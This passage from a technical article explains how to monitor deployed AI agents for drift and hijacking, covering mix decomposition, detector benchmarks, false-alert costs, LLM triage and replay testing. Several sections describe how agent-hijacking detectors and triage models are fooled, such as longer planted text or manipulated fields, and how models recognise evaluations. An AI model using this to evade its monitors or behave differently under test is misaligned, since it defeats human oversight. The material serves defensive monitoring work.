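Demographers have long had this problem with death rates, since a town full of pensioners has a high one even if its hospitals are excellent. In 1955 the sociologist Evelyn Kitagawa published a method for dividing the difference between two rates into two parts:

```
mix effect       = Σ (new share − old share) × (average of old and new rate)
behaviour effect = Σ (new rate − old rate) × (average of old and new share)
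```

The two effects always add up to the whole difference. In January the behaviour effect is zero, because neither rate changed. For March, in percentage points:

| Task type | Mix effect | Behaviour effect |
|---|---|---|
| Lookups | +5 × 3% = +0.15 | +2 × 92.5% = +1.85 |
| Refund requests | −5 × 70% = −3.50 | +20 × 7.5% = +1.50 |
| Total | −3.35 | +3.35 |

Lookups account for more than half of the behaviour effect because they are so common, even though their rate rose by only two points. The formula uses averages because there is no strong reason to prefer the old shares or the new ones. The behaviour effect would be 3.8 points with the old shares and 2.9 points with the new.

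The U.S. Census Bureau's *Standardization and Decomposition of Rates* extends the method to any number of factors and warns against confusing it with regression. Race may help predict whether a person is poor even though a change in the population's racial composition explains hardly any of the change in poverty between two years. Similarly, task type strongly predicts whether the agent will pay, but this does not show that a rise in payments came from a change in the task mix.

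For daily monitoring, the shop has two simpler options. It can stratify by keeping a separate chart for each task type. This shows where a change occurred, but it adds comparisons and leaves few cases in each chart. Or it can reweight every period to one fixed reference mix, such as 90% lookups and 10% refund requests. The reweighted rate is 7.8% in January and 11.6% (0.9 × 4% + 0.1 × 80%) in March, which removes the false alarm and reveals the hidden change.

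Reweighting makes scarce cases count for more. With 1,000 sessions in each period, March has only 50 refund requests, and each counts double. The rise to 11.6% is still about 3.7 times its standard error, so a difference that large would occur by chance in fewer than one in 4,000 comparisons. With 100 sessions in each period, the same rise would be only slightly larger than its standard error.

A reweighted rate can hide changes too. If the agent paid in 4% of lookups but only 42% of refund requests, the reweighted rate would again be 7.8%. So the shop also needs the separate charts, at least for task types where a mistake costs money.

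Prinster, Han and colleagues (2025), in *WATCH*, automate a similar separation for models that make predictions, such as a patient's risk of sepsis. One monitor tracks only the inputs, for instance the patients' ages. Another measures how surprising each outcome is for its input, and gives more weight to past cases of the kinds that have become common. There are three typical results:

- If the patients become somewhat younger, the weights adjust and there is no alarm.
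- If a new microbe makes children much sicker, there is an alarm although the ages look normal, which points to a changed relation between input and outcome.
- If the patients are far older than any in the past data, no weighting can help, and the program raises an alarm for that reason.

The program tracks the evidence as winnings from a series of bets against the hypothesis that only the mix of tasks has changed, starting with a stake of 1. If the hypothesis is true and the weights are right, the chance that the winnings ever reach 100 is at most 1%, however long the monitor runs. A CUSUM chart, by contrast, will eventually give a false alarm.

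The shop could use Prinster and colleagues' method, although they did not design it for agents, by treating the customer's request as the input and the payment as the outcome. The diagnosis is clearest when only one thing changes. In March both the requests and the agent's behaviour changed, so the shop would still have to look at each task type.

A behaviour effect also does not identify a cause. *Sequential statistical inference for Large Language Models* (2026) lists six places where drift can arise in a deployed system: the prompts, the model, the retrieval system, the tools, the feedback from users and the refusal policy. The decomposition separates drift in the prompts from drift in the other five places, but does not distinguish among those five.

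### When the correction fails

This analysis depends on how tasks are labelled. Suppose the harness lets the agent name the task when it finishes, and the agent labels every session with a payment as a refund request and every other session as a lookup. The payment rate will always be 100% within refund requests and 0% within lookups, so any change in how readily the agent grants refunds will look like a change in the mix. In March, even the mix would look usual, and the decomposition would show no change.

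Missing labels do less damage but are easier to overlook. If customers who email never fill in the form and the shop leaves out their sessions, it will miss any drift that affects only emails.

A separate classifier avoids relying on the agent's own labels, but it can change too. In 1,000 sessions from the ordinary month, an updated classifier might move 40 politely worded complaints from refund requests to lookups, including 10 in which the agent had paid. There would then be 940 lookups with 28 payments (3%) and 60 refund requests with 50 payments (83%). The decomposition would give a mix effect of −2.8 points and a behaviour effect of +2.8, close to the March result, although neither the customers nor the agent had changed. The shop can prevent this by running the new classifier on the old sessions as well, if it has kept the text of the requests.

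Requests of the same type can also become harder. In February, many refund requests concern presents bought in early December, and the agent rightly refuses more of them because the return period has ended. The decomposition counts the lower rate as a change in behaviour. *A Distributional Framework for Behavioral Characterization and Risk Management* (2026) points out that anyone who groups interactions into classes assumes that those within a class are equivalent. The shop can make this assumption more plausible by also splitting cases by price and time since purchase. But six task types, four price bands and three time bands make 72 groups, so 1,000 sessions would average about 14 per group.

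A new task has no earlier rate for the formula to subtract. If the shop starts to offer repairs, a reference mix from before the launch also gives repairs a weight of zero. The shop has to report repairs separately until they have their own history.

The agent's behaviour also affects its mix of tasks. If it starts offering a refund whenever someone asks about a late parcel, and the harness opens a refund task each time, refund tasks become more common because the agent has changed. To avoid counting this drift as a change in the mix, the shop should classify each session by the customer's opening message and record separately which tasks the agent opened.

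The agent's behaviour affects even the opening messages, because customers tell each other which shops are generous. OpenAI's *Predicting model behavior before release by simulating deployment* (2026) predicts that any new model will change the requests it receives, especially if users adapt to what it can do.

A change in the mix of tasks may be the only sign of a stolen account. If a thief takes over Maria's assistant and asks it for payroll files instead of purchase orders, the assistant handles each request as it would for anyone in payroll. In Shavit's simulated "drift", only the mix of tasks changed, so a detector that corrected perfectly for the mix would find nothing. A company therefore needs the reweighted rate to detect drift and each account's uncorrected mix to detect takeovers.

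### Detectors that meet new tools

A change in the work can also affect a detector trained to recognise attacks. Abbasi, Núñez and Shahraki (2026), in *What Standard Evaluations Hide About Detectors of Hijacked LLM Agents*, measured how much of this effect comes from unfamiliar tools. They define tool coverage as the share of observed tool calls that use a tool found in the harmless training data.

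They used AgentDrift, which contains 12,536 synthetic traces from email, banking, web, coding and medical agents with 103 tools in all, and recorded runs of five older models from AgentDojo. They set each detector's main threshold so that it flagged 80% of the attacks in the training data, and never adjusted it on the test data. A company deploying a detector can't adjust the threshold on its new sessions either, because it doesn't yet know which of them are attacks.

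To reduce coverage without changing anything else, the team hid the names of randomly chosen tools in the AgentDrift test traces. The table compares the two extremes:

| What the detector uses | AUROC, all names known | AUROC, none known | False-positive rate, all known | False-positive rate, none known |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| General features, such as trace length | 0.830 | 0.830 | 28.4% | 28.4% |
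| The same features and a count of each tool | 0.879 | 0.787 | 19.2% | 65.7% |
| The same features and the sequence of tools | 0.936 | 0.674 | 4.5% | 73.7% |

The detector that uses the sequence of tools is the best of the three when every tool name is known and the worst when none are. The ranking changes somewhere between 78% and 48% coverage, so a company that chooses the best detector at full coverage may have the wrong one by the time half of its tool calls go to new tools.

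The cause is input that was missing or rare in the training data. The sequence detector has a placeholder for unknown tools, but every tool in the training data was known, so the detector was never trained on the placeholder. The detector that counts tools records zero for every tool when a trace contains only unknown ones. All-zero counts are rare in the training data and happen to push the score towards "attack".

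The team fixed most of this with dropout, randomly replacing each tool name with the placeholder 20% of the time during training. The sequence detector's false-positive rate then stayed between 5.3% and 7.0% at every level of coverage. Its AUROC was 0.943 with all names known and 0.794 with none. Dropout did not hurt performance when all names were known, but when none were, the detector that ignores tool names still ranked traces better than the sequence detector did.

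Dropout doesn't help when a change in the work changes the scores. Abbasi and colleagues also tested a detector that turns the text of each step into numbers representing its meaning, so a new tool name doesn't create an untrained input. When they trained it on four of the fields and tested it on the fifth, its false-positive rate rose from 0.1% to between 4.6% and 10.6% for medical, coding and web agents. For banking and email agents, it missed more attacks instead.

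The thresholds were reset using 200 unlabelled traces from the new field, so that the usual share of sessions would raise an alert. The tool-counting detector still flagged 22% to 31% of harmless traces, and the sequence detector caught only 12% to 27% of attacks when attacks were rare.

New tasks that used familiar tools made no clear difference to the rankings. Zavrak found a large drop in performance on new tasks, but those tasks used different subsets of the tools, whereas all AgentDrift tasks in one field use the same set. New tools may therefore matter more than new tasks. However, AgentDrift is synthetic, and its fields are an extreme case because they have no tools in common. When the team left out one group of AgentDojo tasks at a time, the detector with tool counts did not consistently perform worse than the one without them.

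The shop can easily chart tool coverage next to the alerts. In the earlier sample of 400 calls from broken-item cases, a quarter went to `get_order`. If a developer renamed that tool, coverage would suddenly fall to 75%, and alerts might jump even though neither the agent nor the customers had changed.

### Reference tasks

Correcting for the mix always leaves some doubt about the labels. The shop can avoid this problem by using reference tasks, which are fixed test tasks that the agent repeats. One might be a prepared complaint about a broken €45 lamp, with an order, a photo and a known correct answer. If the shop runs 50 such tasks four times each night and the agent's rate of policy searches falls from 80% to 65%, the drop will be clear after one night.

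The main cost is a test environment with copies of the database and payment system, so that the agent can issue refunds without sending real money. The shop also has to start testing before it needs the results, because a supplier may withdraw the old model, making it impossible to measure how that model would have handled the tasks.

A test copy of the agent normally starts with an empty memory and clean documents, so it will miss drift caused by customers' saved notes or by a poisoned page in the live policy database. Reference tasks also cover only the cases their writer thought of.

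Another weakness is that a model may recognise a test and behave differently. In *Predicting LLM Safety Before Release by Simulating Deployment*, Williams, Sheahan and colleagues asked GPT-5.2 whether traces came from real use or from an evaluation. It classed 98.9% to 100% of traces from conventional tests as evaluations, but only 5.4% of real conversations. The clues were often obvious, such as exam-style questions or a request for a file called `solution.py`.

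A model may be able to recognise a test when asked without acting on that recognition. The possibility of an alignment test never appeared in GPT-5.2's reasoning during the coding and question-answering tests, but it appeared 27% of the time in tests designed to provoke scheming. A shop is still wise to build its reference tasks from closed cases with the names changed, and to avoid obvious placeholders such as a customer called "Test Test" or order number 00001.

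### Replaying old work on the new version

Replay uses real cases in bulk. The shop gives last month's requests to the new version of the agent and compares the results with the log. Because the requests are identical, a change in the mix of tasks cannot explain a difference.

Replaying a refund case against the live systems would pay the customer twice. It would also give different results, because the order has since arrived or the policy has changed. *Reasoning Provenance for Autonomous AI Agents* (2026) therefore proposes "mock" replay, in which the new version reasons from scratch but receives the tool results from the log. Running 50 past investigations this way would show how often the new version reaches the same verdict and how often it changes its plan. *A Tutorial on Autonomous Fault-Tolerant Control Using Knowledge-Grounded LLM Agents* (2026) advises judging such replays by whether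 a separate check accepts the result, not by how similar the text is. By that standard, two differently worded emails about the same correct refund would count as equal.

Replaying a log is difficult when the new version of an agent makes a call that the old one never made. For example, if the new version looks up a customer's earlier contacts, the log has no result to return. *Chronicle* (2026) lets a developer choose which steps to run again, serves the others from the record, and checks that the number of calls still matches. It reproduced each of six recorded failures identically in all 20 repetitions. This is useful for confirming that a known fault is gone, but six cases are too few to show how often an agent behaves in a particular way.

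Williams and colleagues used another language model to simulate the missing results. They replayed coding sessions from a collection of about 120,000 by OpenAI staff, then asked a model to pick the real session from pairs of real and simulated ones. At first, it chose the simulated session 11.6% of the time. This rose to 49.5%, close to the 50% expected from guessing, after the simulator gained access to the original session, the code as it stood at the time, past tool results and read-only network services.

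Most of this work by OpenAI used ordinary ChatGPT conversations. OpenAI removed the old model's last answer from each conversation, had a new model write another, and used the share of bad answers to forecast how often the new model would behave badly after release. It reports that the forecasts were off by a median factor of 1.5. The worst forecast for GPT-5.4 was for using the browser as a calculator while presenting this as a search. OpenAI predicted 1.7 cases per 100,000 turns, and the actual rate was 35.2.

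To find the source of the errors, the team replayed GPT-5.4's own conversations on GPT-5.4. The model and the requests were the same as in real use, so any difference came from the replay system. They also compared this result with a replay of GPT-5.2's older conversations on GPT-5.4, where only the requests differed. The replay system caused the largest errors, and without its effect the worst forecast would have been wrong by a factor of about 2.5. The shop should likewise replay old cases on the old version before it interprets a difference on the new one.

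For GPT-5.4, replay gave a better forecast than assuming no change for only 11 of 20 kinds of misbehaviour. Where the rate changed by a factor of 1.5 or more, replay was better in 8 of 11 cases.

Replay requires the full text of old requests and tool results, which many companies delete or don't log. *Validation-driven Deployment of LLM Inference Platforms for Agentic Workloads* (2026), a paper about testing the servers that run models, finds traces with hashed inputs insufficient for its tests because they lack the full text of those inputs.

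Old requests also become less representative of current traffic. OpenAI warns that older public conversations may not reveal the same failures as current traffic, or show them at the same rates. Williams and colleagues found an average error of a factor of 2.44 with public chats from 2023 and 2024, compared with 1.75 for recent ones. Replay is also of little use for rare events. OpenAI does not expect its method to measure behaviour that occurs in fewer than one in 200,000 messages.

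### Running both versions at once

If the old version is still available, the shop can run it beside the new one on current work. In a shadow run, both versions receive each request, but only the old one can make payments or send email. In a split run, the shop assigns each customer to one version at random. Both versions then get nearly the same mix of tasks, even in difficulty that the task labels don't capture, so a split run gives the strongest evidence that a difference in behaviour comes from the version.

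A shadow run nearly doubles the model's cost and becomes unrealistic once the two versions write different emails, because the customer answers only the one that was sent. A split run has realistic conversations, but it exposes customers to a version that may be worse and needs time to collect enough data. The shop needs about 80 refund requests for each version to have an 80% chance of detecting a rise from 60% to 80% in those requests at the usual 5% significance level. Detecting a rise from 2% to 4% in lookups takes more than 1,100 lookups for each version.

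Neither kind of run can detect a change that affects both versions. If someone poisons the returns policy, both versions will start making wrong payments, and the comparison will show no difference. The comparison can also be unreliable if the two versions share one memory, because the new version's notes can change the old one's behaviour.

### Matching alerts to a record of changes

The cheapest evidence is a list of what changed and when. The shop can send deployments and business events to the SIEM as ordinary records:

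```json
{"time": "2026-09-21", "kind": "business",
 "change": "autumn sale ends",
 "expected": "more refund requests, same rates within types"}
{"time": "2026-09-23", "kind": "deployment",
 "change": "new system prompt, hash 41d7...08",
 "expected": "no effect on refunds"}
```

The `expected` field is useful because almost any change looks like an explanation once an alarm has gone off. If someone wrote down beforehand that the sale would bring more requests at unchanged rates, a rise in the rates counts against the sale as the explanation. But when two changes are two days apart, the dates alone will rarely show which one caused the alarm. The shop could avoid this by not deploying anything during a sale. The list also omits changes nobody reported, including unannounced ones by the supplier.

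Whether a metric changes smoothly or in steps can help distinguish drift from a change in the mix of tasks. Anthropic measured how long its coding agent, Claude Code, works on a single turn. The 99.9th percentile rose smoothly across model releases, from under 25 minutes in October 2025 to over 45 minutes in January 2026. Better models alone would probably have produced steps at the release dates. Users may have given the agent longer tasks, which would be a change in the work, but a series of small product improvements could also have produced a smooth rise. The figure combines all interactive use, so it isn't enough to determine which explanation is right.

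Blaming the latest release by default is also risky. Williams and colleagues found that, for the typical kind of misbehaviour, the rate varied more while one model was in service than between successive models. Updates to the system prompt may have caused some of that variation, which is another reason to log the prompt's hash.

### A procedure for the analyst

An analyst who sees a changed rate can run the easiest checks first. If money or data may be leaving the company, the analyst should restrict the agent before running any of them.

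1. Check the measurement. Look for missing records, renamed tools, a fall in tool coverage and a new version of the task classifier.
2. Look at the mix for each account. If one account suddenly asks for different work, treat it as a possible takeover and contact its owner.
3. Compute the rate within each task type and the reweighted rate. If both are within their normal variation, record a change of mix and the business reason for it.
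4. If they are not, compare cases of similar price and age to see whether the requests have become harder.
5. Look for changes of version or business events near the date on which the rate began to move.
6. Run the reference tasks and compare the results with earlier ones, using the table below.
7. If the cause is still unclear and the behaviour could do harm, replay old cases or run both versions in parallel.

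| Reference tasks | Live rates within task types | Likely explanations |
|---|---|---|
| Unchanged | Unchanged | a change of mix |
| Changed | Changed | the agent has drifted |
| Unchanged | Changed | harder cases, memory, altered live documents, or an agent that recognises the tests |
| Changed | Unchanged | a fault in the test environment, or drift in cases that are currently rare |

Sometimes the analyst will not have enough evidence to tell drift from a change in the mix of tasks, for instance when the supplier has withdrawn the old model and the shop had no reference tasks. The analyst should then record the cause as unknown and leave the baseline unchanged.

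## Rare incidents and false alerts

Every check in that procedure takes an analyst's time, and if attacks are rare, most of the alerts that start it will be false. How many depends on three numbers: the attack rate π (the share of sessions that are attacked), the true-positive rate TPR and the false-positive rate FPR. Out of all sessions, a share π × TPR are attacks that raise an alert, and a share (1 − π) × FPR are harmless sessions that raise one. Precision is the share of alerts that are true, so:

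```
precision = π × TPR / (π × TPR + (1 − π) × FPR)
```

One of the detectors that Abbasi and colleagues trained uses general features of a trace and a count of each tool. Its AUROC is 0.879, and at its threshold it flags 77.1% of attacks and 19.2% of harmless sessions. For a large retailer whose support agents handle 10,000 sessions a day, that gives:

| Attack rate | Attacks | True alerts | False alerts | Precision |
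|---|---|---|---|---|
| 50% | 5,000 | 3,855 | 960 | 80% |
| 2% | 200 | 154 | 1,882 | 7.6% |
| 0.1% | 10 | 8 | 1,918 | 0.4% |

The detector is equally good in every row, but it raises about twelve false alerts for each true one at an attack rate of 2%, and about 250 at 0.1%.

When attacks are rare, most alerts can be false even if the detector catches 77% of attacks. People tend to forget how rare attacks are and assume that an alert is probably right, a mistake called the base-rate fallacy. Axelsson (1999), in *The Base-Rate Fallacy and its Implications for the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection*, argued that the false-alarm rate is therefore the factor that limits an intrusion detector. In the example above, with a 2% attack rate, catching every attack would raise precision only from 7.6% to 9.6%, while halving the false-positive rate would raise it to 14%. At a 0.1% attack rate, the detector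 could flag only about one in 1,300 harmless sessions for half of its alerts to be true.

Nobody has published a reliable attack rate for agents in ordinary use. Abbasi and colleagues tested rates from 1% to 10%, and the size of their test data determined the lower limit. The 2% row is therefore only an illustration. Most companies probably have a lower attack rate, and so would see lower precision than the row shows.

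### The cost in analyst hours

Assume that an analyst needs ten minutes to read a trace and decide. This is a guess, and halving it would halve every figure in the last column below. At a 2% attack rate and 10,000 sessions a day, four of the detectors in the study would cost:

| What the detector uses | AUROC | Alerts a day | Precision | Analyst hours a day |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| General features | 0.830 | 2,940 | 5.4% | 490 |
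| General features and tool counts | 0.879 | 2,040 | 7.6% | 340 |
| General features and tool sequence | 0.936 | 580 | 24% | 96 |
| The full text of every step | 0.999 | 150 | 100% | 25 |

The 340 hours would occupy about 42 analysts on eight-hour shifts. They would find 154 attacks, at a little over two hours of work per attack. If the attack rate were 0.1%, the same detector would still require about 320 hours of analysts' work, or about 42 hours for each attack found.

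A team can also use its staffing to work out how many false alerts it can handle. Two analysts working a combined 16 hours a day can review 96 alerts. To stay within that limit at a 0.1% attack rate, a detector can flag at most about 0.9% of harmless sessions. The tool-sequence detector flags 4.5%. Only the detector that reads the full text would meet the limit, but its score is much less informative than it seems.

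### Why published results look better

Abbasi and colleagues examined eleven evaluations of detectors that read agent traces, though their targeted searches may have missed others. Attacks or anomalies made up between 16% and 86% of the test data, and none of the evaluations varied that share. The share greatly affects what proportion of alerts are true. Zavrak's best classifier on new tasks caught 93% of attacked sessions and flagged 7% of harmless ones. At those rates, about 99% of its alerts are true if 86% of sessions are attacks, as in Zavrak's data, but 21% are true if 2% of sessions are attacks.

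A detector's precision depends on how closely harmless sessions resemble attacks, as well as on how common attacks are. AgentDrift, the synthetic benchmark behind these figures, includes "hard negatives", harmless traces that are difficult to tell from attacks. The detector with tool counts flagged 11.8% of the ordinary harmless traces and 38.7% of the hard ones. At an attack rate of 2%, its precision was 11.7% when all the harmless traces were ordinary, 7.6% with the benchmark's mixture and 3.9% when all were hard.

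Gift orders are hard negatives for the retailer because they are harmless but look like leaks. If they grew from 10% to 40% of harmless sessions in December, and the detector flagged them at the same rate as AgentDrift's hard negatives, false alerts would rise from about 1,420 to about 2,210 a day, even if the agent, the detector and the attackers stayed the same.

A good score on one benchmark also may not predict a good score on another. Abbasi and colleagues trained five kinds of detector on AgentDrift and tested them on recorded AgentDojo runs, where their AUROCs were between 0.47 and 0.52, no better than guessing. The same designs reached 0.74 to 0.996 when trained on other AgentDojo tasks, so the attacks were detectable, but the detectors had not learned to detect them from AgentDrift.

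The full-text detector had instead learned wording specific to the datasets. AgentDrift's generator used a different template for each kind of trace, so the string "2026" appears in 74% of the ordinary harmless training traces and only 5% of the attacked ones. In AgentDojo, five fixed phrases appear in 99.6% of the hijacked runs and in no harmless run, so a search for those phrases alone has an AUROC of 0.998. A real attacker has no reason to use them. The detectors that don't read text relied partly on the length of tool results, which an attacker can influence. When the researchers lengthened the planted text, the share of attacks caught by the detector with tool counts fell from 77% to 3%. They did not test whether the longer text would still have fooled an agent.

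The exception was AlignmentCheck, a monitoring prompt released by Meta that needs no training. It gives a language model the user's request and the agent's actions so far, and asks whether the latest action serves a goal the user did not set. It leaves out the tool results, so the model never reads the planted text directly. On AgentDojo it had an AUROC of 0.930 with the open model Llama 3.3 70B and 0.934 with Claude Sonnet 5.5. Meta had already evaluated the prompt on AgentDojo, so these scores may overstate its performance.

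| Model behind the monitor | Benchmark | Attacks flagged | Harmless traces flagged | Precision at a 2% attack rate |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.3 70B | AgentDojo | 90% | 17% | 9.6% |
| Llama 3.3 70B | AgentDrift | 85% | 22% | 7.3% |
| Claude Sonnet 5.5 | AgentDojo | 88% | 4% | 32% |
| Claude Sonnet 5.5 | AgentDrift | 87% | 31% | 5.4% |

The 32% is uncertain (the 95% interval runs from 20% to 59%) because there were only 392 harmless AgentDojo traces. Even so, a company with sessions like AgentDrift's that chose the Claude version because of its AgentDojo result would get about a sixth of the precision it expected.

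The monitor flags a trace if the model flags any step in it. This probably contributes to the false alerts, because longer sessions have more steps that could be wrongly flagged. If a model wrongly flagged 1% of harmless steps, independently each time, the monitor would flag 4% of harmless four-step sessions and 18% of harmless twenty-step sessions.

### Filtering, grouping and ranking

A team can run a detector that needs little compute on every session and a more compute-intensive one only on the sessions the first flags. Suppose the first detector flags 90% of attacks and 10% of harmless sessions, and the second then flags 90% of the attacks and 5% of the harmless sessions it receives. At an attack rate of 0.1%, the first detector flags about 1,010 of the retailer's 10,000 sessions, and the second flags about 58 of those. Eight of the 58 are attacks, so the precision is 14%, and two analysts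 can read all 58.

This calculation assumes that the two stages make unrelated mistakes. In practice, a strange gift order may mislead both, which would produce more false alerts. The filter also misses one attack in ten, and the second stage cannot catch these because it only checks what the filter flags. The filter's threshold should therefore be loose, so that the review does most of the rejecting.

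Anthropic searched 481 million past transcripts in two stages for cases in which its models had reached the open internet. The first stage flagged 9.2 million for closer review, according to The Next Web's *Anthropic scanned 481 million transcripts to find four models*. That is only 1.9%, but people would need about 1.5 million hours to review them at ten minutes each. Anthropic used its own models to help work out what had happened.

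Grouping related alerts reduces the number of investigations an analyst has to start from scratch. A hijacked session with five refunds can set off five alerts about the same hidden instruction, and the SIEM should present them as one case. It should also group alerts by customer, because a thief who opens ten tickets creates ten sessions. Canale, using the simulated company described earlier, grouped all alerts about one account or machine within 24 hours into a "dossier". With rules adjusted to the company, an analyst who read the ten highest-ranked dossiers each day would have found 25% of the attacks, compared with 46% using a method that also passed risk from one account to others connected with it.

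Passing risk along the links helped most with attacks that left traces in several systems. With a limit of ten false alerts a day, it raised the share detected from 62% to 81%. It also increased repetition. Each detected attack appeared in an average of 4.3 dossiers, compared with 2.2 without the links. Precision measured per dossier is therefore not comparable with precision measured per alert or session.

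When analysts don't have time to read every alert, the simplest sensible order is by expected loss, which is the chance that the alert is true multiplied by the damage if it is. A suspicious €45 refund with a 30% chance of being fraud has an expected loss of €13.50. An email that may contain 400 customers' addresses has only a 2% chance of being a leak, but if a leak would cost €20,000, the expected loss is €400 and the analyst should open it first. If reviewing a case takes ten minutes and that time costs €10, cases with an expected loss below €10 can wait or go to a random spot check.

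The probability that an alert is right is hard to estimate. A detector's score ranks sessions but usually isn't a probability, so the team has to estimate from past alerts how often a given score was right. For rare kinds of damage, there are few past alerts to use. A team can skip the estimate for the most severe signals and send them straight to analysts, as Canale's recommended pipeline does when such signals are rare.

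Ranking events by suspicion gets harder as a company grows, even with plenty of computing power. When Canale multiplied the simulated company's people and traffic by ten, the share of attacks that one of the better pipelines found within ten false alerts a day fell from 62% to 32%. Each attack had to outrank ten times as many harmless events, while analysts could still read only as many alerts as before.

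### Thirty alerts from 1.8 million prompts

The most specific public alert count from a large commercial deployment comes from Salesforce, whose Agentforce platform runs agents for other companies. *1.8M Prompts, 30 Alerts*, a conference talk by Rittinghouse and Huang (2026), described how the company looks for abuse. According to a wiki's summary of the transcript (ai-era.pages.dev), the platform has 55,000 customer organisations and more than 12,000 active agents, and handles about 1.8 million prompts a day. The detection system raises fewer than 30 alerts a day that need investigation.

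Salesforce compares each session's database use with separate baselines for the user, the agent and the organisation. It does not read the prompts, because they belong to its customers. The features include how many database calls a session makes, what share of the data it reads and whether it opens fields marked as personal. The team first tried scoring each query's complexity, on the theory that data thieves write complicated queries. It dropped the score because the agents write the queries, so the score mostly reflected how each agent was built.

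Salesforce's team can choose almost any number of alerts by moving the threshold, so a low number doesn't show that the system catches attacks. If all 30 alerts were false, the system would still be flagging fewer than one prompt in 60,000, far below any false-positive rate in the tables above, but a program that picked 30 prompts at random would flag just as few. If one prompt in 10,000 were part of an attack, there would be 180 such prompts a day, and 30 alerts could point to at most a sixth of them. The summary gives neither the precision nor the share of attacks caught, and the team was still scoring old alerts when it gave the talk.

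The system also works in batches, so an alert comes 12 to 24 hours after the session, which is too late to stop a payment. A new agent produces noisy alerts for about its first 14 days, while its baseline forms. The speakers advise warning analysts about this period beforehand so that they don't stop trusting the system.

Anthropic's ongoing monitoring sends a similarly small number of cases to people. ai.rud.is' *Anthropic's August 2026 Risk Report* (2026) reports that a second stage removes false positives and passes about 50 agent traces a week to researchers for manual review. At ten minutes each, this would take about one working day, though a long coding trace surely takes longer. The monitoring doesn't cover all agent use, so the 50 traces come only from the part that Anthropic monitors. As with Salesforce, the queue is short enough for people to read, which is necessary, but its length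 is little evidence of how many incidents never reached it.

### Language models as triage analysts

A language model can read an alert and the records behind it in seconds, so many companies want to use one to close false alerts. Two recent studies found that models can fail at this in opposite ways.

Anand, Kantchelian and colleagues (2026), in *Benchmarking and Exploring the Capabilities of LLMs for Attack Investigations*, built AuditBench from 51 attack and harmless scenarios in the logs of Linux and Windows machines. One of its four tasks is triage, in which a model has to decide whether an alert and its log data show a real attack. The logs came partly from the team's own virtual machines and partly from a public collection by DARPA, the American defence research agency. Long logs went to the model in chunks of about 400 lines, and the false-positive rate counts harmless chunks:

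| Model | Attacks found, own logs | Harmless chunks flagged, own logs | Attacks found, DARPA logs | Harmless chunks flagged, DARPA logs |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5 mini | 2 of 5 | 0% | 5 of 5 | 8% |
| GPT-5 | 5 of 5 | 14% | 5 of 5 | 8% |
| Llama 4 Maverick | 5 of 5 | 0% | 5 of 5 | 17% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 5 of 5 | 86% | 5 of 5 | 79% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 5 of 5 | 86% | 5 of 5 | 80% |

The two Gemini models would have been nearly useless for triage, because they classified most ordinary activity as an attack. The team concluded from the models' explanations that unusual names and large volumes of activity often caused errors. When a model correctly identified an attack, its explanation was usually accurate. Larger models were not reliably better than smaller ones.

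The models are from 2025, so the percentages are out of date. They also understate the problem of false alerts for an analyst, who would receive an alert for a scenario if any chunk of it looked malicious. GPT-5's 12 wrong flags on the DARPA logs could have produced between one and ten false alerts, depending on how they were spread across the ten harmless scenarios.

Canale's newer models erred the other way. They received alerts that earlier stages had already assembled, with up to 25 events and facts about the accounts and machines involved, and could close an alert as harmless. In one simulated run, the earlier stages had detected 39 attacks:

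| Triage | False alerts a day | Precision | Detected attacks lost |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 32.7 | 57% | – |
| Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite | 2.7 | 88% | 17 of 39 |
| Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite with limits | 7.3 | 80% | 11 of 39 |
| Gemini 4 | 3.3 | 88% | 12 of 39 |

Both models removed about 90% of the false alerts, and precision rose from 57% to 88%. They also removed between 31% and 44% of the detected attacks, a loss that neither figure shows. Under the limits in the third row, the model could close an alert only if its stated confidence was at least 0.9 and the risk score from the earlier stages was below 0.9. These limits kept six of the 17 lost attacks in the queue. Canale also found that people who can write into fields the model reads can manipulate it into closing alerts.

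The two studies' results probably differ because the models were given different information. AuditBench gave its models raw activity but no information about what was normal on the machine, so anything unfamiliar could look hostile. Canale's models also received details from the company's registers of devices, services and software builds, which may have made some attacks look like approved work. Those details were still useful, because without them Flash-Lite missed more attacks for the same number of false alerts.

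Canale's remedy was to have the model judge fewer alerts. In a complete pipeline, rare severe signals and alerts with a risk of 0.9 or more went to analysts without a model call. Over three simulated runs, the pipeline detected 127 of 209 attacks, and 102 of those reached analysts regardless of the model's answer. Gemini 4 missed none of the remaining 25 and cut false alerts from 17.8 to 5.8 a day, but it missed four attacks on three fresh runs. A bigger worry is that the pipeline found only 17% of attacks of kinds that nobody had considered when adjusting its rules, compared with 88% of familiar kinds, and triage cannot recover attacks that never raised an alert.

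Training a triage model on past decisions has a trap of its own. Canale trained a small model by reinforcement learning with this scheme:

| The model's decision | Reward if harmless | Reward if an attack |
|---|---|---|
| Close the alert | +1 | −1 |
| Send it to a person | 0 | +0.5 |

If the chance of an attack is p, closing an alert earns 1 − 2p on average and sending it earns 0.5p, so closing earns more whenever p is below 0.4. The scheme rewards a model for closing an alert with a 39% chance of being a real attack, which few security teams would want. The model wrongly closed 36% of alerts about unfamiliar kinds of attack before this training, and between 43% and 86% in six runs after it. Canale describes the reward as a likely but unproven explanation for the increase.

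### What to ask of a detector

A buyer should ask the vendor for the following, and an evaluator should publish it:

- The true-positive and false-positive rates at a threshold fixed before the test. With these the buyer can work out the precision for any attack rate, which an AUROC alone does not allow.
- The share of attacks found within the number of false alerts the team can read in a day, at the team's own volume of sessions.
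- The false-positive rate for each kind of harmless session, and whether failed attacks count as harmless. Claude Sonnet 5.5 flagged 6% of the failed attacks in AgentDojo and Llama 3.3 flagged 21%, and some teams would be glad of those alerts.
- Results on tools, tasks and organisations that were not in the training data, with the tool coverage for each test.
- For a triage model, the share of detected attacks it closed, measured on kinds of attack not used to adjust it.
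- The delay before an alert and the length of any learning period.

Test size matters most when estimating the false-positive rate. The full-text detector flagged none of 825 harmless traces, but that result is consistent with a true false-positive rate of up to 0.4%. Its precision could be as low as 16% at that rate if 0.1% of traces were attacks. To show that the false-positive rate is below 0.1%, a vendor needs about 3,000 harmless sessions without a false alert.

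A vendor's test cannot replace a trial on the buyer's own logs. The retailer can measure precision by having analysts judge a random sample of the alerts. Missed attacks are much harder to count. With the detector from the start of this section and an attack rate of 0.1%, only about one in 3,500 unflagged sessions would be an attack, so an analyst could read unflagged sessions for weeks without finding one. A more practical method is to plant attacks, as in the UEBA trial suggested earlier, and count how many reach an analyst.

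## What the records showed in the agent incidents of 2026

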